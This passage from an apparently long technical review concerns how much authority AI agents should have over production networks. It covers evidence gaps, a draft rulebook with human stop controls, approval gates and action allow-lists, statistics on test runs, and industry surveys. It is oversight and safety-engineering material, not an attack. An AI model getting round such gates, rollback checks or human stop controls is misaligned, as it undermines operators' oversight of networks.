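Coverage is how much of the changed code the tests exercise. The operator sets the weights α, β and γ. The gate refuses any change that scores above the limit for the agent's level. Because the terms are added, a familiar, well-tested change to every core router can score lower than a new kind of change to one spare port. A separate cap on the blast radius would fix this weakness.

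### Where the published evidence runs out

The 13 systems are spread unevenly across the levels:

| Level | Systems | Where researchers evaluated them |
|---|---|---|
| Read-only assistant | 1 | Connected to production |
| Analyst | 7 | Five connected to production, one in a controlled setting, one early live prototype |
| Write-limited planner | 5 | One in an operational case, four in controlled settings |
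| Closed-loop controller | 0 | |

Four of the five planners carried out changes within set limits. None had an independently assessed rollback mechanism. The numbers are small, and the table reflects only published evidence, so it may omit systems that companies use but have never described publicly.

*SoK* (Li, Li and colleagues, 2026) found a similar gap in evidence about speed. It reviewed 139 groups of papers on software that makes network decisions, including many systems without a language model. Fifty of these groups claimed that their software was fast enough for a control loop or a time limit, but only four supported the claim with matching measurements.

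Speed matters because faults often occur together. Suppose an agent takes eight seconds per decision and has a ten-second limit. It passes a test with one request, but if a new request arrives every five seconds, the second waits three seconds and finishes 11 seconds after it arrives, and each later one takes longer. Li and colleagues measured a more extreme case, in which every decision met a ten-second limit when handled alone, but none did when about five requests arrived per second.

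### Four requirements for operators

Zhang and colleagues conclude that the evidence does not yet support giving agents direct authority over a network from request to result. They set out four requirements for using agents at all:

1. The agent's ability to draft a change stays separate from the authority to commit it.
2. Each proposal has a form that software can check against policies, invariants and the device's data model.
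3. The operator can deploy the change in a controlled way, monitor it and recover.
4. A record links the request to its inputs, the checks, the actions and the outcome.

The commit tool in the Junos MCP server fails the first requirement because the same call delivers the model's draft and commits it. A log that records only commands would fail the fourth because it leaves out why the agent sent them.

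These safeguards also have to work across vendors and fail safely when measurements are missing. Zhang and colleagues add that evidence can expire. If the model, its prompt or its workflow changes, the operator may have to test again and should reduce the agent's authority in the meantime.

### Thirteen rules for a repair agent

The most detailed proposal for agents that act alone is the governance draft by Smith and Pai, who work for the networking company Arrcus. It covers software that detects a fault on a device, asks a language model for advice and makes the repair without individual approval. These are its 13 principles:

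| Principle | Main rule |
|---|---|
| Human authority | A person can stop the agent at once, and an agent that cannot reach anyone only monitors |
| Do no harm | If unsure, do nothing and alert a person |
| Management plane protection | Never put management access at risk |
| Minimum necessary action | Use the least disruptive repair, on one target |
| Bounded autonomy | Stay within limits on pace, scope and risk |
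| Transparency | Record every action, prompt and response |
| Reversibility | Prefer repairs that the agent can undo |
| Graceful degradation | Make no repairs if the model, alerts, log or measurements fail |
| Escalation | Call a person after repeated failures or a rollback |
| Limits on the model | The model only advises, and software accepts only actions from a fixed list |
| Safe start-up | Repairs stay off until an operator changes two settings |
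| Absolute prohibitions | Ten things remain forbidden whatever the operator's settings |
| Review | People review the rules before deployment, after incidents and regularly |

Suppose R4's interface towards R3 is producing errors, and the model suggests switching it off and on. The repair would go like this:

1. Software checks that the action is on both the developer's list and the operator's, and that its risk is within the limit. Smith and Pai rate a brief interruption like this as medium, the highest risk the agent may take alone by default.
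2. It checks that the interface is not a protected target. Loopback interfaces are protected as well as management ones. If the check itself fails, the software treats the interface as protected.
3. It saves the interface's current state. If it cannot, the repair stops here.
4. It switches the interface off and on.
5. It takes fresh measurements from the interface. If the fault has not improved, it restores the saved state and calls a person.

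The fifth step is the weakest because it checks only the resource that the agent changed. After the OSPF cost change on R1, the interface would look healthy even though the offices' web traffic was taking the detour. An operator would need to add tests of the whole network.

The rules permit much less than the agents in most demonstrations do:

| Job | Under the draft |
|---|---|
| Restart one BGP session | The agent may do this alone if the operator has listed it and the fault is serious enough |
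| Raise the OSPF cost on R1 | A person must approve it, under the default settings |
| Add a loopback address | Forbidden |
| Edit R2's route filter | Forbidden |
| Replace the OSPF key on four routers | Forbidden |

Smith and Pai also forbid arbitrary command-line input, which rules out an agent that types freely over SSH. They rank changing a routing cost as a more disruptive repair than switching an interface off and on, which is open to question. The cost change can affect more of the network, but it usually moves traffic with less loss.

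The draft has no official standing. Anyone can submit one to the IETF, and no working group has adopted this one. It appears to have only one version, numbered 00, which expired on 25 September 2026. Discussion continues elsewhere, and Wu, Ceccarelli and colleagues submitted another individual draft, *Problem Statement for Observability, Intervention and Control (I&C) in Multi-Agent Autonomous Networks*, in July 2026.

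### What a series of clean runs proves

The rule of three, used above for the 111 switches, also applies to an agent's test runs. If an agent causes harm in a fraction p of its runs, and the runs are independent, the chance of seeing no harm in n of them is (1 − p)ⁿ. The 95% upper limit is the value of p at which that chance falls to 5%:

```
(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n
```

The 3 comes from the natural logarithm of 0.05, which is −2.996.

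| Runs without harm | Upper limit on the harm rate |
|---|---|
| 20 | 14% |
| 88, as in ANI-Gamut | 3.3% |
| 300 | 1% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |
| 300,000 | 0.001%, or 1 in 100,000 |

If an agent makes 20 changes a day and 1% of them cause harm, it makes a harmful change every five days on average. At a rate of 1 in 100,000, the target that Bracciale and colleagues set, it makes one about every 14 years.

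One harmful run raises the limit to about 4.7/n, so the agent would need roughly 470 runs in total to support "below 1%". If the operator fixes the agent instead, the count restarts from zero, because the earlier runs tested a different agent.

The limit also holds only if the tests detect all harm. NetConfArena's tests, for example, mostly did not check for damage outside the task. If tests miss half of the harmful changes, the limit doubles to 6/n.

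### Why 300 runs may be worth 22

Test runs often resemble each other. An operator might build ten network templates and run 30 versions of each, with different addresses. If an agent handles one version safely, it will probably handle the others safely too, so they add less evidence than 30 unrelated jobs. A standard correction for this is:

```
effective runs = n / (1 + (m − 1) × ρ)
```

Here m is the number of runs per template, and ρ measures how alike their results are, from 0 for unrelated to 1 for identical. In NetConfArena, about 43% of the variation in scores was between templates. If harm followed the same pattern, ρ would be about 0.43, and the 300 runs would give about as much information as 22 independent runs. The upper limit would then be about 13% instead of 1%.

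An operator should grant authority separately for each kind of job, because the 300 runs may include only a few of some kinds. If only 15 involve routing policy, the limit for that kind of job is 18%.

More computing power does not solve this. At ten minutes each, 300,000 runs would take almost six years on one emulated network and three weeks on 100 copies, but most would repeat situations the designers had already thought of. Bracciale and colleagues expect failure rates on production hardware to differ from those in their emulation, so they rely on comparisons between interfaces rather than the rates themselves. Shadow operation supplies real jobs, but the agent's commands never reach a device.

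The calculation doesn't hold when someone is attacking the agent. Attackers can keep trying until they find text that misleads it, so the share of harmless logs in a test is a poor guide to the logs the agent will read during an attack.

### Matching the evidence to the possible damage

An operator can work backwards from the harm that is tolerable. Suppose a company accepts an average loss of 0.1 user-hours per change, where one user-hour is one person without service for an hour:

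| Job | Worst case | Highest tolerable harm rate | Clean runs needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Move one user's port | 1 user for an hour | 10% | 30 |
| Change a switch with 100 users | 100 users for an hour | 0.1% | 3,000 |
| Change a core routing policy | 10,000 users for an hour | 0.001% | 300,000 |

Limiting the damage can replace a lot of testing. If a confirmed commit reliably ended the core outage after two minutes, the worst case would fall from 10,000 user-hours to 333, and the agent would need 10,000 clean runs instead of 300,000. That reliability is a strong condition because rollback fails when the tests miss the fault. Averaging also counts one large outage the same as many small ones that add up to the same harm, which an operator that carries emergency calls should not accept.

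### The case for acting sooner

People make many mistakes on networks and can be slow to repair them. Cisco's *The Impact of Agentic AI on Network Operations* (2026), which summarizes a survey of IT and network staff, reports that the median incident takes 12.5 hours to resolve. The mean is 88 hours because some incidents last more than a week. Staff close 46% of alerts without investigating them.

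Smith and Pai argue that a missed repair generally costs less than a wrong one, which is why their agent does nothing when it is unsure. Whether that is true depends on how long people take to respond. If a correct repair saves T hours of outage, a wrong one adds H hours, and the agent is right with probability p, acting is better on average when:

```
p × T > (1 − p) × H,   which means   p > H / (T + H)
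```

| Time a correct repair saves | Time a wrong repair adds | How often the agent must be right |
|---|---|---|
| 1 hour | 4 hours | More than 80% |
| 12.5 hours | 4 hours | More than 24% |
| 1 hour | 5 minutes | More than 8% |

In the NIKA tests, GPT-5 identified the cause of a fault 55% of the time, which would justify acting in the second and third rows but not the first. This result is a strong argument for more autonomy where staff respond slowly or rollback is quick. However, many incidents in Cisco's survey are performance problems, and a wrong repair can turn a slow service into an outage.

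In the same survey, Cisco found that 92% of performance problems crossed the boundaries between areas such as networking, security and cloud services, and that teams used nearly ten tools to monitor them. An agent with read-only access could search all of those tools, which could reduce much of the delay without any new authority to make changes.

### What the 80% in Cisco's survey means

Desmond (2026), in *80% of network pros are OK with giving AI an autonomous role*, splits the survey's best-known result into 56% who would accept an autonomous role for AI only if a person approves the agent's actions and 24% who would accept it without human oversight. Most of the 80% would therefore accept only something close to C1. In answer to a separate question, 82% said they would let AI make at least some kinds of production change by itself, though they may have meant very minor ones.

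The figures on current use are less clear. Desmond reports that 51% of respondents already use agents to take corrective action in production. Cisco applies that figure only to organisations that use AI, about three quarters of the total, so the share of all organisations would be nearer 38%. The two accounts also differ on the number of respondents, 1,000 or 1,396.

Cisco's *From Signal to Action* reports that senior IT leaders want trust to come before more autonomy. The survey's respondents asked for approval gates, policy limits, a way to override the agent and records that nobody can alter. Cisco has a commercial interest in how much authority agents receive, and the report promotes its own system for running networks with them. The respondents' willingness to use agents is not evidence that the agents are safe.

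Zeus Kerravala, an industry analyst whom Desmond interviewed, expects agents to make mistakes, "but a lot fewer than people will", and compares them to self-driving cars. He may be right, but the comparison rests on crash records from public roads, and the 13 systems in Bilal and colleagues' review have no similar records. Every copy of a model may also misread the same command, whereas two engineers rarely make the same mistake on the same day, and an average error rate doesn't capture this disadvantage.

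*From automated response to reasoning* (Phillips, 2026) argues for autonomy within set limits, with checkpoints for engineers, and cites an average downtime cost of $15,000 a minute. That cost applies to outages caused by an agent's mistakes as well as to slow repairs. At that rate, an agent that wrongly takes a network down for 20 minutes would cost $300,000.

### What Meta and others let agents do

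Confucius, at Meta, is the best-documented production system that goes beyond diagnosis. Wang, Lin and colleagues (2025) report in *Intent-Driven Network Management with Multi-Agent LLMs* that it had been running for two years and that teams had built more than 60 applications on it.

Zhang and colleagues describe Confucius as turning an engineer's request into a graph of steps that reuse Meta's existing procedures and tools. The model therefore arranges known operations and does not have to invent commands for each device. Software verifies and validates the workflow before any step that could change the network. Zhang and colleagues place Confucius at C2, the highest level they give any assistant or workflow agent in their comparison, but the model still has no authority to commit a change.

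Two years of use is good evidence that engineers find the system practical. It does not give a harm rate, which would require counting the changes and how many went wrong. The 60 applications also differ in what they can affect, since some help with planning and others with live operations.

Other production systems in the same survey stop earlier:

| System | What the model does | Who acts on the network |
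|---|---|---|
| Confucius, Meta | Arranges existing tools and procedures into a workflow | The workflow, after validation |
| BiAn, Alibaba Cloud | Ranks the devices most likely to have caused a failure and explains why | Engineers |
| NetAssistant, ByteDance | Matches an engineer's question to a prepared diagnostic procedure | Engineers |

These companies have unusually good test networks and analysis software, but they give their agents less freedom than many of the survey's respondents say they would accept. If 51% of AI-using organisations really let agents make repairs in production, most of that experience is unpublished, so other operators cannot use it as evidence.
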